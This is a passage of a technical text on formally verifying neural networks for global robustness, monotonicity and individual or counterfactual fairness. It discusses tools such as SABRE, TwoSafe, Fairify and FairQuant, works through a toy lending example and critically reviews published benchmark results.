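The verifier has proved the requirement once it has proved every case. It usually splits on a single ReLU, creating one case where the weighted sum is at least 0 and one where it is at most 0. The ReLU is linear within each case, so it needs no relaxation there. If the verifier splits every undecided ReLU, no relaxation remains, and the search can determine whether the requirement holds. Choosing the right neurons to split keeps the number of cases down.

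RABBit, another verifier from 2024, adds branching to the ideas behind RACoon. Suresh, Banerjee and Singh, in *Relational Verification Leaps Forward with RABBit*, point out that splitting several runs jointly limits how finely each run can be divided, because every combination of cases counts. If a verifier has time for 10,000 cases, it can divide each of two runs into only about 100 cases by splitting them jointly, but 5,000 by splitting them separately. For four runs, the figures are 10 and 2,500.

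RABBit therefore splits runs in two ways. One part splits all the runs together and recomputes the joint bounds for each case. The other computes joint bounds once at the start, then splits each run separately. A final MILP combines the results. Suresh and colleagues report that the combination works better than either part alone. They also report that joint splitting gives tighter bounds than RACoon, which doesn't split, and α,β-CROWN, which splits but ignores the links between runs.

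### Splitting on the sign of a difference

RABBit splits individual neurons, while SABRE, the verifier of Fukuda and colleagues, splits on whether a neuron's weighted sum is larger in the first run or in the second. These cases are d ≥ 0 and d ≤ 0. If d ≥ 0, then D lies between 0 and d, which is one of the two triangles in the parallelogram, and the other case gives the other triangle. When l = −u, the triangles together cover half the area of the parallelogram. For example, if l = −0.1 and u = 0.1, the parallelogram allows D to be as large as 0.05 at d = 0, while the triangles force it to be 0.

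A network with two inputs between −1 and 1 shows the effect:

N(x₁, x₂) = ReLU(x₁ + x₂) − ReLU(x₁ − x₂).

Let each input move by at most 0.1. The weighted sums then move by d₁ and d₂, which each lie between −0.2 and 0.2. If the inputs move by a and b, then d₁ = a + b and d₂ = a − b. The parallelograms allow the output to rise by 0.5(d₁ − d₂) + 0.2 = b + 0.2, which can be as much as 0.3. Splitting on signs gives three cases:

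- If d₂ ≥ 0, the second ReLU can't fall. The first rises by at most 0.2, so the output rises by at most 0.2.
- If d₂ ≤ 0 and d₁ ≥ 0, the output rises by at most d₁ − d₂ = 2b, which is at most 0.2.
- If d₂ ≤ 0 and d₁ ≤ 0, the first ReLU can't rise. The second falls by at most 0.2, so the output again rises by at most 0.2.

So the output rises by at most 0.2, and it rises by exactly that much when the input moves from (0.5, 0.5) to (0.6, 0.6). Swapping the two runs shows that the output can't fall by more than 0.2 either.

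Splitting a neuron in one run makes its ReLU exact there but leaves the same neuron undecided in the other run. Splitting it in both runs creates up to four cases, while splitting on the sign of the difference between the runs creates two and narrows that difference directly. In a small example by Fukuda and colleagues, splitting a single neuron gave a range of −0.15 to 0.15 for the change in the output, while splitting on the sign of the same neuron's difference gave −0.067 to 0.15.

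### What SABRE can't prove

SABRE is sound but incomplete, so it can't prove some true requirements, however long it runs. Once it has fixed the sign of every difference, it has nothing left to split, but each D can still be anywhere in its triangle.

We can see this by fixing x₁ at 0 in the same network. The output becomes ReLU(x₂) − ReLU(−x₂), which equals x₂, so it changes by at most 0.1. But if x₂ rises by 0.1, the triangles allow the first ReLU to rise by 0.1 and the second to fall by 0.1, which changes the output by 0.2. This can't happen in the real network, because only one of the two ReLUs is on at a time. Splitting on the individual ReLUs rules it out, but knowing the signs of the differences doesn't.

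Fukuda and colleagues accept this limitation because hard problems usually have more differences than can be split in the time allowed. They leave combining both kinds of splitting to future work.

### How much the new splits help

They tested SABRE on 817 global robustness problems, using ACAS Xu networks and classifiers for MNIST, CIFAR-10 and GTSRB, a dataset of German traffic signs. Time limits ranged from 7 minutes for ACAS Xu to 2 hours for the hardest images. RaVeN ran on every problem first, and the other methods then ran on those it couldn't solve. No version of RABBit was available for global robustness, so they built two methods that split individual neurons, one of which closely follows RABBit's strategy. The table shows the better of the two in each row.

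| Problems | Total | Solved by RaVeN | Added by splitting single neurons | Added by SABRE |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu | 230 | 42 | 12 | 67 |
| MNIST, fully connected | 156 | 31 | 27 | 54 |
| MNIST, convolutional | 156 | 23 | 8 | 27 |
| CIFAR-10 | 158 | 10 | 31 | 23 |
| GTSRB | 117 | 9 | 24 | 33 |

RaVeN and SABRE together solved 319 of the 817 problems, or 39%. SABRE added 204 of these, about twice as many as either of the other splitting methods. To choose which difference to split, SABRE uses the linear program to estimate how much each possible split would tighten the final bound. When Fukuda and colleagues replaced this estimate with a random choice, SABRE added only 116 solutions.

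CIFAR-10 was the exception. When the two images could differ by at most 1/256 per pixel, SABRE solved 5 problems and the other two methods solved 16 each. At 3/256, SABRE solved 8 and the others 4 each. If the inputs are very close, the parallelograms are already small, so cutting them in half gains little. The CIFAR-10 network also had many more undecided ReLUs than the other image networks.

The problems differ in how much of the input space they cover. For ACAS Xu, the two inputs can be anywhere in the benchmark's range of flight conditions. For the image networks, both images must be close to one given picture, differing from it by at most 12/256 per pixel, so a proof covers only pairs of images near that picture. The MNIST limits of Wang and colleagues are looser but apply to the whole input domain.

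### What the experiments imply for fairness and monotonicity

Most of these experiments test global robustness or one disturbance applied to many images. In both cases, many input features change by a small amount. Attribute-flip fairness and monotonicity usually compare runs that differ in only one feature, possibly by a large amount.

A verifier that tracks differences can compute tighter bounds when the two runs share inputs. In the toy lender, the second ReLU cancels when only s changes, as it did in the product network, so the verifier finds the exact range: flipping s from 0 to 1 raises the score by between 0 and 1. Computing a separate range for each copy would only show that the score rises by at most 3 or falls by at most 2.

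This also proves one half of the fairness requirement. Since the flip never lowers the score, nobody the lender approves with s = 0 would be refused with s = 1. The other half fails, as we saw with applicants (1, 0) and (1, 1). In general, if a flip moves the score by at most B, the decision can change only for applicants whose score is within B of the cut-off.

RACoon's approach also carries over. To show that nobody loses approval when s changes from 0 to 1, we need to prove for every x that the lender refuses (x, 0) or approves (x, 1). This has the same form as proving that every disturbance leaves at least one of two images correctly classified, with the applicant's finances x in place of the disturbance. With equal weights, the average of the two margins is

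½(0.5 − f(x, 0)) + ½(f(x, 1) − 0.5) = ½(f(x, 1) − f(x, 0)),

which is half the difference between the two runs. The difficulty is scale. The image experiments allow only tiny disturbances, while x ranges over all possible applicants, and linear limits become much looser over such a large region.

In one experiment with SABRE, Fukuda and colleagues limited the changes in 45 problems to random subsets of the inputs. When 12.5% of the inputs could change, SABRE solved 41 problems and the two methods that split single neurons solved 39 and 40. When all inputs could change, SABRE solved 24 and the others 15 and 17. So SABRE's advantage may be small for requirements that change a single input, although it still needed about half as many subproblems in the 12.5% case. The changes were small here too, so the experiment can't show what happens when an attribute flips completely.

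For monotonicity, splitting on the sign of a difference can only help after the first layer. If one input rises and the others stay fixed, every weighted sum in the first layer changes by its weight on that input times the rise, so we already know the sign of each difference.

The toy lender has a single layer of two ReLUs, and its score is the first minus the second. If x rises by d, each ReLU rises by between 0 and d, so difference bounds alone allow the score to fall by as much as d. To prove that it never falls, we have to look at when each ReLU switches on. The first is on when x is above 1 − s and the second when x is above 1. Since s is never negative, the first is on whenever the second is, so it rises at least as much and the score can't fall.

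## Why does a strict global rule force a constant classifier, and what repairs it?

The strict version of global robustness requires any two nearby inputs to get the same class:

for all u, u′ in D: if every coordinate of u is within ε of the same coordinate of u′, then h(u) = h(u′).

This looks like a natural thing to ask of a classifier, but only a network that gives everyone the same answer can satisfy it.

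### A chain of short steps

The straight line between any two inputs u and v in a box can be cut into steps so short that no coordinate changes by more than ε in one step. The rule requires both ends of each step to have the same class, so u and v have the same class. The classifier is therefore constant on the box.

In the toy lender with s = 1, the score equals x up to x = 1. With ε = 0.1, we can walk from x = 0 to x = 1 in ten steps. The lender refuses at x = 0.4 and approves at x = 0.5, so that step breaks the rule. A smaller ε only lengthens the chain. With ε = 0.001 it has a thousand steps, and one still crosses from refusal to approval.

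The domain can be any connected set (all in one piece), not only a box. Let S be the set of inputs that can be reached from u in steps of at most ε. Two inputs within ε of each other are either both in S or both outside it, so S has no edge inside the domain and must be all of it. Only a gap wider than ε can stop the steps from reaching every input. For example, if a feature records age in whole years and ε is half a year, people of different ages are never within ε of each other, so the class can change with age without breaking the rule.

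### The fairness rule collapses too

Two applicants rarely match exactly on everything except sex, so some fairness rules allow a tolerance on the other attributes. Using uₛ for the protected attribute and uᵣ for the rest, the rule becomes

for all u, u′ in D: if uₛ ≠ u′ₛ and uᵣ is within ε of u′ᵣ, then h(u) = h(u′).

The rule compares people only across groups, but two comparisons are enough to link neighbours in the same group. If r and r′ are within ε of each other, the rule requires (r, 0) to have the same class as (r′, 1), and (r′, 1) to have the same class as (r′, 0). So (r, 0) and (r′, 0) have the same class, and the chain argument applies again.

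A lender that approves everyone with x of at least 1 and ignores s breaks the rule when ε = 0.1, because it refuses (0.95, 0) and approves (1.05, 1), even though it doesn't discriminate by s. With ε = 0, the rule only compares (r, 0) with (r, 1). The chain can't move from r to any other value, so the class can depend on r in any way. This version of the rule is called attribute-flip fairness, and the lender satisfies it.

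### Limiting how far the scores move

Global robustness with a tolerance δ on the scores, |N(u) − N(u′)| ≤ δ, does not force a constant classifier, because small changes can add up along the chain. Ten steps can move the score by up to 10δ.

The rule no longer directly constrains decisions, but it still protects the decision for any input whose score is more than δ from the cut-off. With several class scores, the top score must lead by more than 2δ, since it may fall by δ while another rises by δ.

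A proved δ is also informative only when compared with the typical distance between scores and the cut-off. If we divide the toy lender's score and its cut-off by 10, every decision stays the same, but the largest change in the score becomes ten times smaller.

### An extra class for unstable inputs

Another repair lets the classifier decline to answer. Leino, Wang and Fredrikson (2021), in *Globally-Robust Neural Networks*, add a class ⊥, meaning "not robust here", and require that

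for all u, u′ within ε of each other: h(u) = ⊥, or h(u′) = ⊥, or h(u) = h(u′).

A chain can now get from one class to another, but it has to pass through a strip of ⊥ at least ε wide.

They build such a classifier from an ordinary one. Let Kᵢ be a Lipschitz bound on how fast the score yᵢ can change. If j is the winning class, the score of ⊥ is

y_⊥ = the largest value of yᵢ + (Kᵢ + Kⱼ)r over all i ≠ j.

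This is the highest score a rival could reach relative to the winner within distance r, if the rival's score rose as fast as possible while the winner's fell as fast as possible. If the winner's score is above y_⊥, no input within r gets another class. Setting r = ε/2 gives the global rule. Two inputs at most ε apart have a midpoint within ε/2 of both, so if neither gets ⊥, both have the midpoint's class.

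For the toy lender with s = 1, let the approval score be f and the refusal score a constant 0.5. The approval score changes at a rate of at most 1, so for ε = 0.1 the new classifier refuses below x = 0.45, approves above 0.55 and outputs ⊥ in between.

In a large network nobody knows the exact rates, so Leino and colleagues multiply the spectral norms of the layers, where a layer's spectral norm is the largest factor by which it can stretch a vector. In the toy lender, both layers have norm √2, so the product is 2, although the true rate is 1. The strip then runs from 0.4 to 0.6, twice as wide as necessary. Training reduces this excess because no training example has ⊥ as its correct label, so ordinary training penalises every ⊥ and pushes the network towards smaller bounds. On the MNIST digits, Leino and colleagues reached 63% verified accuracy against changes of Euclidean length up to 1.58,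 meaning that the network both correctly classified and certified 63% of the test images.

The repair lets the network output ⊥ instead of a class, so a network that always outputs ⊥ satisfies the rule without classifying anything. Ideally, the network outputs ⊥ only on inputs unlike any real data. Boetius and Leue count this as an advantage in some applications, since an image of pure noise has no correct class.

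The guarantee also fails if a computed K is too small. Power iteration, the usual way to compute a spectral norm, approaches the true value from below, so stopping early can produce a false certificate. Tobler, Syeda and Murray (2025), in *A Formally Verified Robustness Certifier for Neural Networks (Extended Version)*, showed that in certain circumstances earlier certifiers are unsound in ways an attacker can exploit. They wrote their own certifier in Dafny, a language whose compiler checks proofs about the code.

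### Splitting the domain by categories

Categorical features, such as the type of housing an applicant has, put natural gaps in the domain. We can apply the strict rule only to pairs that agree on all of them:

for all u, u′ in D: if the categories match and the numbers are within ε, then h(u) = h(u′).

The chain argument now works separately for each combination of categories. A network can satisfy the rule without being constant, but numerical features such as income can't affect its decisions. Athavale and colleagues say two earlier fairness verifiers, CertiFair and Fairify, work this way. They object that this approach can't handle classifiers whose class depends on continuous inputs, which is the normal case for robustness. The approach also never compares pairs of inputs with different categories, so it can miss violations between categories.

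### Requiring agreement only when the network is confident

Their own repair, from 2024, excuses inputs on which the network is unsure. A classifier with scores z₁, …, zₙ for n classes usually turns them into probabilities with the softmax function,

softmax(z)ᵢ = e^(zᵢ) / (e^(z₁) + … + e^(zₙ)),

and the largest of these is its confidence. For a threshold k, the rule is

for all u, u′ in D: if u and u′ are close and conf(u) > k, then h(u) = h(u′).

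The same formula covers robustness and fairness, with a different definition of "close" for each. For robustness, two inputs are close if every numerical feature is within its tolerance and the categories match. For fairness, they are close if the protected attributes differ and the rest are within tolerance.

The chain breaks at inputs where the network has low confidence. Inputs of different classes that the network classifies confidently must be more than 2ε apart, since otherwise it would have to assign both classes to their midpoint.

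Whether the toy lender counts as fair depends on how confidence is defined. With a refusal score of 0.5 and an approval score f between 0 and 1, its confidence never exceeds 62%. At k = 0.7, the rule therefore never applies, and the lender counts as fair although it refuses (1, 0) and approves (1, 1).

Multiplying both scores by 10 changes no decisions but raises the confidence at those two inputs to 99.3%, so the lender fails the fairness rule at k = 0.9. It does pass the robustness rule at k = 0.9 and ε = 0.1, because an input is confident only if f is more than 0.22 from the cut-off, and changing both inputs by up to 0.1 moves f by at most 0.2.

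Athavale and colleagues acknowledge that a network can count as safe merely because its confidence is low. They answer that an accurate network should also be confident, and that matching confidence to accuracy, known as calibration, is a separate field of research.

### What the softmax approximation costs

Marabou can't handle softmax, which is not piecewise linear, so Athavale and colleagues replace it in two steps. Let M be the largest score among the rivals of class i, and let Sig(t) = 1/(1 + e⁻ᵗ) be the sigmoid. Then

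Sig(zᵢ − M − ln(n − 1)) ≤ softmax(z)ᵢ ≤ Sig(zᵢ − M).

The upper bound is exact if all rivals but one have negligible scores, and the lower bound is exact if all rivals are tied. The paper has a plus sign before the logarithm, but its proof is valid only with a minus sign. The second step replaces the sigmoid with 35 straight segments that stay within η = 0.005 of it.

The lower estimate, less η, then serves as the network's confidence. To see how far off it can be, write α = e^(M − zᵢ). The two bounds are 1/(1 + (n − 1)α) and 1/(1 + α), and they are furthest apart at α = 1/√(n − 1). Adding the error of the segments gives the margin

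b = (n − 2)/(√(n − 1) + 1)² + 2η.

To certify the rule for true confidence above k, we have to prove it for approximate confidence above k − b. The soundness theorem also requires approximate confidence above ½, so k must be at least ½ + b. With two classes, the first term of b is zero and k can be as low as 0.51. The minimum rises to 0.68 with three classes and 0.84 with five. With ten, the first term is exactly 0.5, so k would have to exceed 1 and the theorem guarantees nothing.

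Much of this loss comes from using the worst-case margin everywhere. For ten classes, the bounds are furthest apart at 0.25 and 0.75, and much closer together near 1. The TwoSafe tool from *Differential Zonotopes for Verifying Global Robustness of DNNs* (Athavale, Teuber and colleagues, 2026) avoids the fixed margin. If the confidence is above k, the top score must lead the second by more than ln(k/(1 − k)), which is 4.6 for k = 0.99. This condition is linear in the scores and needs no approximate sigmoid. Some inputs with confidence below k also meet this condition, but none with confidence below k/(k + (n − 1)(1 − k)).

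The table compares the two methods for k = 0.99, leaving out the small term 2η. A proof that has to cover lower confidence levels needs more pairs to agree and is more likely to fail for a network that satisfies the rule.

| Classes | Fixed margin | Lowest confidence covered, 2024 method | Lowest confidence covered, TwoSafe |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 0 | 0.99 | 0.99 |
| 3 | 0.17 | 0.82 | 0.98 |
| 5 | 0.33 | 0.66 | 0.96 |
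| 10 | 0.50 | 0.49 (theorem does not apply) | 0.92 |

### Proofs on four datasets

The 2024 experiments used networks of up to 50 neurons, trained on four public datasets. German Credit has 1,000 loan applicants, whom the network sorts into good and bad risks. On Adult, the network predicts whether a person earns more than $50,000 a year, and on Law School, whether a student will pass the bar exam. COMPAS contains risk assessments of criminal defendants, divided into three classes.

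The fairness checks gave these results:

| Network | Protected attribute | Threshold k | Result | Time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| German Credit | gender | 0.5 | proved | 10 seconds |
| German Credit | age | 0.5 | proved | 11 seconds |
| COMPAS | gender | 0.5 | violated | 7 seconds |
| COMPAS | ethnicity | 0.5 | violated | 18 seconds |
| COMPAS | ethnicity | 0.99 | violated | 26 seconds |
| COMPAS | ethnicity | 0.999 | proved | 171 minutes |

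For COMPAS and ethnicity, Athavale and colleagues ran the real network on the counterexample and found a confidence of 0.969. They conclude that the network is unfair at thresholds below 0.969 and fair above 0.999, but the range in between is undecided.

The violation is certain, but the proof at 0.999 is hard to reconcile with the paper's theorem. To certify 0.999 with three classes, the tool has to prove the rule for approximate confidence above about 0.83. By the bounds above, the known counterexample, whose true confidence is 0.969, has an approximate confidence of at least 0.93, so that proof would have failed. The tool must have checked a higher threshold, and then the theorem doesn't certify the rule at 0.999.

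In the robustness checks, the German Credit network had counterexamples at confidence thresholds below 0.7 but none above 0.75, even for large input distances. The proofs for the other three networks succeeded at all confidence thresholds above 0.5, and each took 50 seconds or less.

That success is suspicious for Adult and Law School, which have two classes. The larger of two probabilities is always at least 0.5, and it equals 0.5 only when the scores are tied. If ties always go to the same class, then whenever the class changes between two neighboring inputs in a chain, at least one of them is not tied, and the rule applies to it. The confidence rule with k = 0.5 is therefore the same as the strict rule. Taken literally, the result means that each of these two networks gives the same answer to all inputs that share the same categories, whatever their numerical features are. Because the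 sigmoid is approximate, the class could still change where the confidence stays below about 0.51.

The accuracies fit this reading. The paper reports 0.77 for Adult and 0.94 for Law School, but not the share of each class. In the standard version of Adult without incomplete rows, about 75% of people earn $50,000 or less, and about 95% of the students in the original law school study eventually passed the bar. A classifier that always predicts the more common class would therefore score about 0.75 and 0.95, though different preprocessing could shift these figures somewhat. The proofs were probably fast more because the networks are nearly constant than because of the method.

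The German Credit network's accuracy of 0.71 is also close to the 70% of applicants whom the dataset labels as good risks, but the robustness counterexamples show that its answer changes between nearby inputs. The network is therefore not constant, so that can't be why its fairness proofs succeed. By the chain argument, these proofs make sense only if the applicant's other attributes had to match exactly.

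### Requiring both runs to be confident

In the 2024 rule only one of the two inputs has to be confident. A confident input must not have *any* neighbour of another class, even one on which the network is almost undecided. TwoSafe can also check a weaker, symmetric rule:

for all u, u′ in D: if u and u′ are close, conf(u) > k and conf(u′) > k, then h(u) = h(u′).

This is the same as the rule of Leino and colleagues if ⊥ stands for "confidence at most k". Confident inputs of different classes only have to be more than ε apart, whereas the 2024 rule requires 2ε.

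The TwoSafe paper illustrates the difference with a classifier that has one input x and the scores x and 0. Its confidence is at least 0.75 when x is at least 1.1 or at most −1.1. With ε = 1.5 the symmetric rule holds, because confident inputs of different classes are at least about 2.2 apart. The 2024 rule fails, because the confident input x = 1.1 has a neighbour, x = −0.4, with a different class.

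The symmetric rule suits systems that send unsure cases to a person. Without that step, it can allow harm. For example, if changing an applicant's sex turned a confident approval into a low-confidence refusal, the rule would allow it, but the applicant would still be denied the loan.

### Larger networks

TwoSafe tracks the two runs together with their difference, like the verifiers in the previous section. Its main addition is a way to describe all pairs of nearby inputs exactly. For an input between 0 and 1 and ε = 0.1, it writes

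u = 0.5 + 0.45a + 0.05b,  u′ = 0.5 + 0.45a + 0.05c,

with a, b and c anywhere between −1 and 1. The shared number a moves both inputs together, and b and c move them apart by at most 0.1. When the bounds are too loose, the tool splits the range of a, b or c. If it simply cut the input's range in two, it would lose every pair with one input on each side of the cut.

According to the TwoSafe paper, the largest network in the 2024 experiments had 15 ReLUs. The new tool handled the three larger networks below, with a time limit of two hours. The table gives the lowest tested threshold at which it proved each rule.

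| Network | Size | ε | 2024 rule | Symmetric rule |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LHC, particle classification | 16 inputs, 80 ReLUs | 0.001 | 0.9 | 0.8 |
| ACAS Xu, collision advice | 5 inputs, 300 ReLUs | 0.001 | 0.7 | 0.6 |
| HAR, activity recognition | 561 inputs, 500 ReLUs | 0.001 | 0.6 | 0.6 |
| HAR, activity recognition | 561 inputs, 500 ReLUs | 0.01 | 0.99 | 0.9 |

The 2024 tool proved none of these. It ran out of time or memory, or reported counterexamples that the real network doesn't have. On ACAS Xu, the proofs at the lowest thresholds took almost two hours, while those at 0.99 took about three minutes, because a higher threshold leaves fewer pairs to check. The tolerances are small; ε = 0.01 is 1/200 of the range of each HAR input.

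Proofs like these may still be vacuous if no input reaches the confidence threshold. TwoSafe searches for such an input during verification and found one for every network except ACAS Xu, so the ACAS Xu proofs may not apply to any real decision.

Kresse, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *Logic Gate Neural Networks are Good for Verification*, avoid softmax by changing the network. Logic gate networks consist of simple operations on bits, such as "and" and "exclusive or". Each class has a block of output bits, and the confidence is the fraction of all the output ones that are in the winning class's block. Both copies of the network and the rule can then be written exactly as a formula of true-or-false variables, and an ordinary SAT solver can search for a pair of inputs that breaks the rule.

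They tested networks with three layers of 50 to 300 gates on the same four datasets and a five-class version of Adult. For fairness, they allowed no difference in the other attributes and searched for the lowest threshold at which the rule holds. Within an eight-hour limit, the search succeeded for gender and ethnicity on every network except the German Credit ones with more than 100 gates per layer. For each threshold found, they also confirmed that at least one input reaches it.

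## Can a network be proved to treat similar people alike?

The fairness proofs so far mostly compared a person with a copy who differs in one protected attribute. This is one of at least three ways to define "treat similar people alike" precisely, and a network can satisfy one definition but fail another.

### Three requirements

Attribute-flip fairness, as before, requires h(r, s) = h(r, s′), where s is the protected attribute and r is everything else about the applicant.

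Dwork and colleagues asked for something broader in *Fairness Through Awareness*. They assume that someone has supplied a distance d(u, u′), which measures how different two people are for the decision at hand. They then require

D(M(u), M(u′)) ≤ d(u, u′) for all u and u′.

Here M(u) gives the probability of each possible decision about person u, and D measures how far apart two such sets of probabilities are. For a lender that approves u with probability p(u), the condition is |p(u) − p(u′)| ≤ d(u, u′). This is the original definition of individual fairness. It is a Lipschitz condition, so Wurm counts it as a case of global robustness, which explains why verifiers for individual fairness reuse robustness tools.

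The probabilities are necessary. If a lender answers only yes or no, p is always 0 or 1, so everyone it approves must be at distance 1 or more from everyone it refuses. When d shrinks smoothly as people become more alike, the chain argument from the previous section implies that such a lender must give everyone the same answer. A lottery whose odds rise gradually with x doesn't have this problem.

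Whether a network counts as fair also depends on d. Suppose the toy lender uses its score f as the probability of approval. If d is |x − x′|, which ignores s, the lender is unfair, because (1, 0) and (1, 1) are at distance 0 but have approval probabilities 0 and 1. If d is |x − x′| + |s − s′|, the lender is fair to everyone, because changing x or s by some amount never changes f by more than that amount.

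So a proof of individual fairness is only as good as the measure of similarity behind it. Dwork and colleagues accepted this, and suggested that a regulator might impose the measure or a civil rights organisation might propose one, and that it should be open to public argument. They argued that every decision rule already treats some people as similar, and that stating this judgement as a formula at least lets others dispute it.

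Most verifiers avoid the dispute with a crude measure that sets d to 0 for two people who differ only in the protected attribute and to 1 for any other pair. The Lipschitz condition then requires equal treatment at distance 0 and nothing at distance 1, since two probabilities can't differ by more than 1. This property is called attribute-flip fairness. It removes the need to justify a scale, but it puts two applicants whose incomes differ by one dollar at the maximum distance.

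Biswas and Rajan (2022), in *Fairify*, propose a compromise called ε-fairness. It is the flip test with a tolerance that the developer picks for each of the other attributes, such as five years for age. The chain argument applies here too, so the decision can't depend on age at all. By setting the tolerances, the developer is in effect choosing which attributes the network must ignore.

### Changing the attribute and everything it causes

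Kusner, Loftus, Russell and Silva proposed counterfactual fairness in 2017. It asks whether a person would have received the same decision if their protected attribute had been different from the start. Answering this takes a causal model, a set of equations for how each feature arises from the attribute A and from background factors that A doesn't influence. The requirement is

P(Ŷ[A←a] = y | x, a) = P(Ŷ[A←a′] = y | x, a)

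for every decision y and every other value a′. Both sides concern the same person, whom we observe with features x and attribute a. On the right, we set the attribute to a′ and recompute every feature that depends on it before asking for the decision Ŷ.

Suppose that pay discrimination lowers the finances of group 1, so that an applicant in group s has finances x = v − 0.5s, where v is a background factor. An applicant with x = 0.7 and s = 1 has v = 1.2. If she had the same v but s = 0, her x would be 1.2. Two simple lenders treat her differently.

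| Approval rule | Flip only s | Change s and recompute x |
|---|---|---|
| x ≥ 1 | passes | fails: refused at 0.7, approved at 1.2 |
| x + 0.5s ≥ 1 | fails: approved with s = 1, refused with s = 0 | passes, since x + 0.5s is always v |

Hardly any lender can pass both tests here. A lender that passes the flip test decides on x alone. If it also passes the causal test, its decision is the same at x and x − 0.5 for every x. If a higher x also never turns an approval into a refusal, the lender has to give everyone the same answer.

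The two tests coincide when the attribute causes none of the network's other inputs, because recomputing then changes only the attribute. That condition is implausible for sex or race when the other inputs include income, occupation and marital status. The names in the literature hide this difference. For example, *FairQuant* (Kim, Wang and Wang, 2024) describes the flip test as a non-probabilistic form of counterfactual fairness.

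A verifier could also check the causal version if the causal model is simple enough. In the example, when the first copy of the network receives (x, 1), the second would receive (x + 0.5, 0) instead of (x, 0), which is one more linear equation between the inputs. The proof would then depend on the equation x = v − 0.5s, and data alone often can't show whether such an equation is right.

### A flip-fair network could do without the attribute

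If a network passes the flip test on every input, we can set the protected attribute s to 0 for every applicant without changing any decision. A proof that it passes therefore shows that it decides exactly as some network without the attribute would. Such a network passes the test automatically, but its other inputs can still act as proxies for the attribute. Suppose 90% of one group lives north of a river, 90% of the other lives south of it, and a lender's network approves only applicants with a northern postcode. The network doesn't take the protected attribute as an input, but it approves 90% of the first group and 10% of the second.

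One reply is that the test was never meant to catch this. A network that accepts a person but refuses them when only their race is changed in the input has a serious fault, whatever other faults it has, and nobody can find that fault by looking at the weights. Biswas and Rajan developed their verifier for networks that are already trained, where deleting a column would mean retraining.

Another reply is to let the proxies vary too. In one query, Biswas and Rajan check whether a network is fair with respect to race when two people can count as similar even if their marital status differs. A network that passes can't depend on marital status either, by the same argument as for ε-fairness. Doing this with postcodes would stop the northern lender, but it amounts to deleting the postcode as well. Many useful features correlate with sex or race to some degree, so there is no natural point at which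 to stop deleting them. Deletion also rules out the second lender in the table above, which needs s to correct for discrimination in pay.

The flip test also takes the trained network as given, so it can't show whether prejudice in the training data shaped a decision. *Analyzing Fairness of Neural Network Prediction via Counterfactual Dataset Generation* (2026) presents a method that checks whether changing a few possibly biased training labels would change the prediction for one person. The method compares networks trained on different data, and a network that never sees the attribute can fail this test.

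### Cutting the domain into boxes

The flip test is almost trivial for a linear classifier, because flipping s shifts every applicant's score by the same amount, the weight on s. In a neural network, the same flip can raise one applicant's score and lower another's. Biswas and Rajan write that John and colleagues (2020) gave verification methods for linear classifiers and for kernel classifiers such as support vector machines, but that these methods don't carry over to neural networks.

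Biswas and Rajan's tool, Fairify, combines the product network with two ways of making it smaller:

1. It cuts the domain into boxes by splitting every attribute that has many possible values. The Adult census data gives 16,000 boxes.
2. Within each box, it looks for ReLUs that are always off. It computes a range for every neuron's weighted sum, then asks a solver about each neuron that the ranges leave undecided. Removing these neurons changes no output inside the box.
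3. It gives the two smaller copies to Z3, a general-purpose logic solver, for up to 100 seconds.
4. If Z3 runs out of time, Fairify also removes neurons that stayed off for 1,000 random inputs and tries again.

Step 4 can change the network's decisions, so a proof that relies on it covers only the pruned network. Biswas and Rajan suggest deploying the pruned network instead of the original.

Biswas and Rajan tested 25 networks, 16 of which came from Kaggle, a site where people share data and code. The networks use German Credit, Adult and a third dataset, Bank, for predicting which bank clients will accept an offer. Without steps 1 and 2, Z3 settled one of the 25 in 30 hours. Fairify settled 19 with a limit of 30 minutes each, and three more when it had an hour and smaller boxes. They call these 22 networks "verified", but the tool found a violation in every one of them and proved none of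 the 25 fair.

The pruning in step 2 removed an average of 11% to 96% of the neurons, depending on the network. In the network where it removed 11%, Z3 settled none of the boxes.

Proving some boxes fair is useful even when the network as a whole is unfair. For one credit network, Fairify proved 199 of 201 boxes fair and found violations in the other two, so the network's owner would know where the unfairness occurs. Kim and colleagues built on this idea with FairQuant, a tool that reports the share of the input domain on which a network is provably fair.

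FairQuant runs an interval analysis twice on each box, once for each value of s. If both ranges of scores lie on the same side of the cut-off, everyone in the box gets the same decision and the box is fair. If the ranges lie on opposite sides, changing s changes the decision for everyone in the box. Otherwise FairQuant splits the box on the attribute that seems to influence the score most. In the paper's example, a hiring network takes an interview score from 1 to 5, the applicant's gender and 0 to 5 years of experience, which makes 30 pairs of applicants who differ only in gender. The first analysis is inconclusive. After one split, FairQuant finds that everyone with an interview score of 4 or 5 gets an offer, so it certifies those 12 pairs, or 40%, as fair.

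FairQuant never compares the two runs with each other, so it misses some easy proofs. Suppose a lender's score is x − 1, which ignores s. For x between 0.9 and 1.1, the scores in both groups range from −0.1 to 0.1, so the box stays undecided. However often we split it, some piece still contains x = 1. A difference bound would prove the lender fair without any splitting, because the difference between the two runs is always 0.

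### Shares of the domain

Kim and colleagues ran both tools for up to 30 minutes on each of 32 networks, 25 of them from the Fairify study. The figures show the range across the networks for each dataset.

| Dataset and attribute | Networks | Hidden neurons | Certified by Fairify | Certified by FairQuant | FairQuant's time |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bank, age | 8 | 18 to 300 | 1% to 77% | 84% to 96% | 0.4 to 71 seconds |
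| German Credit, age | 5 | 9 to 124 | 0% to 99% | 33% to 99.8% | 0.3 to 32 seconds |
| Adult, gender | 12 | 10 to 200 | under 1% | 19% to 91% | 1 second to 8 minutes |
| COMPAS, race | 7 | 24 to 10,000 | 0% to 80% | 97% to 98% | 0.01 to 101 seconds |

FairQuant found counterexamples in all 32 networks. An ordinary verifier can also find them. When Kim and colleagues gave α,β-CROWN a network made of two copies of the original, it found counterexamples within seconds. They object that it then stops without showing how widespread the problem is.

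The COMPAS row is probably less of a breakthrough in network size than it looks, because the domain there seems to be tiny. For each of the seven networks, the share of inputs that FairQuant found to be unfair equals its number of counterexamples divided by 625. For the largest network, 15 counterexamples make up 2.40% of the domain. So the domain apparently contains just 625 pairs of people, and running the network on all 1,250 people would answer the question exactly. The German Credit domain, by comparison, contains more than 435 trillion possible applicants.

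A high certified share can also mean that a network hardly distinguishes between people. The two German Credit networks with the highest shares, 99.65% and 99.80%, are also the least accurate, at 70.67% and 69.33%. A network that called everyone a good risk would be about as accurate. The other three networks are 73% to 75% accurate, and FairQuant certified between 33% and 58% of their inputs.

### Applicants who could not exist

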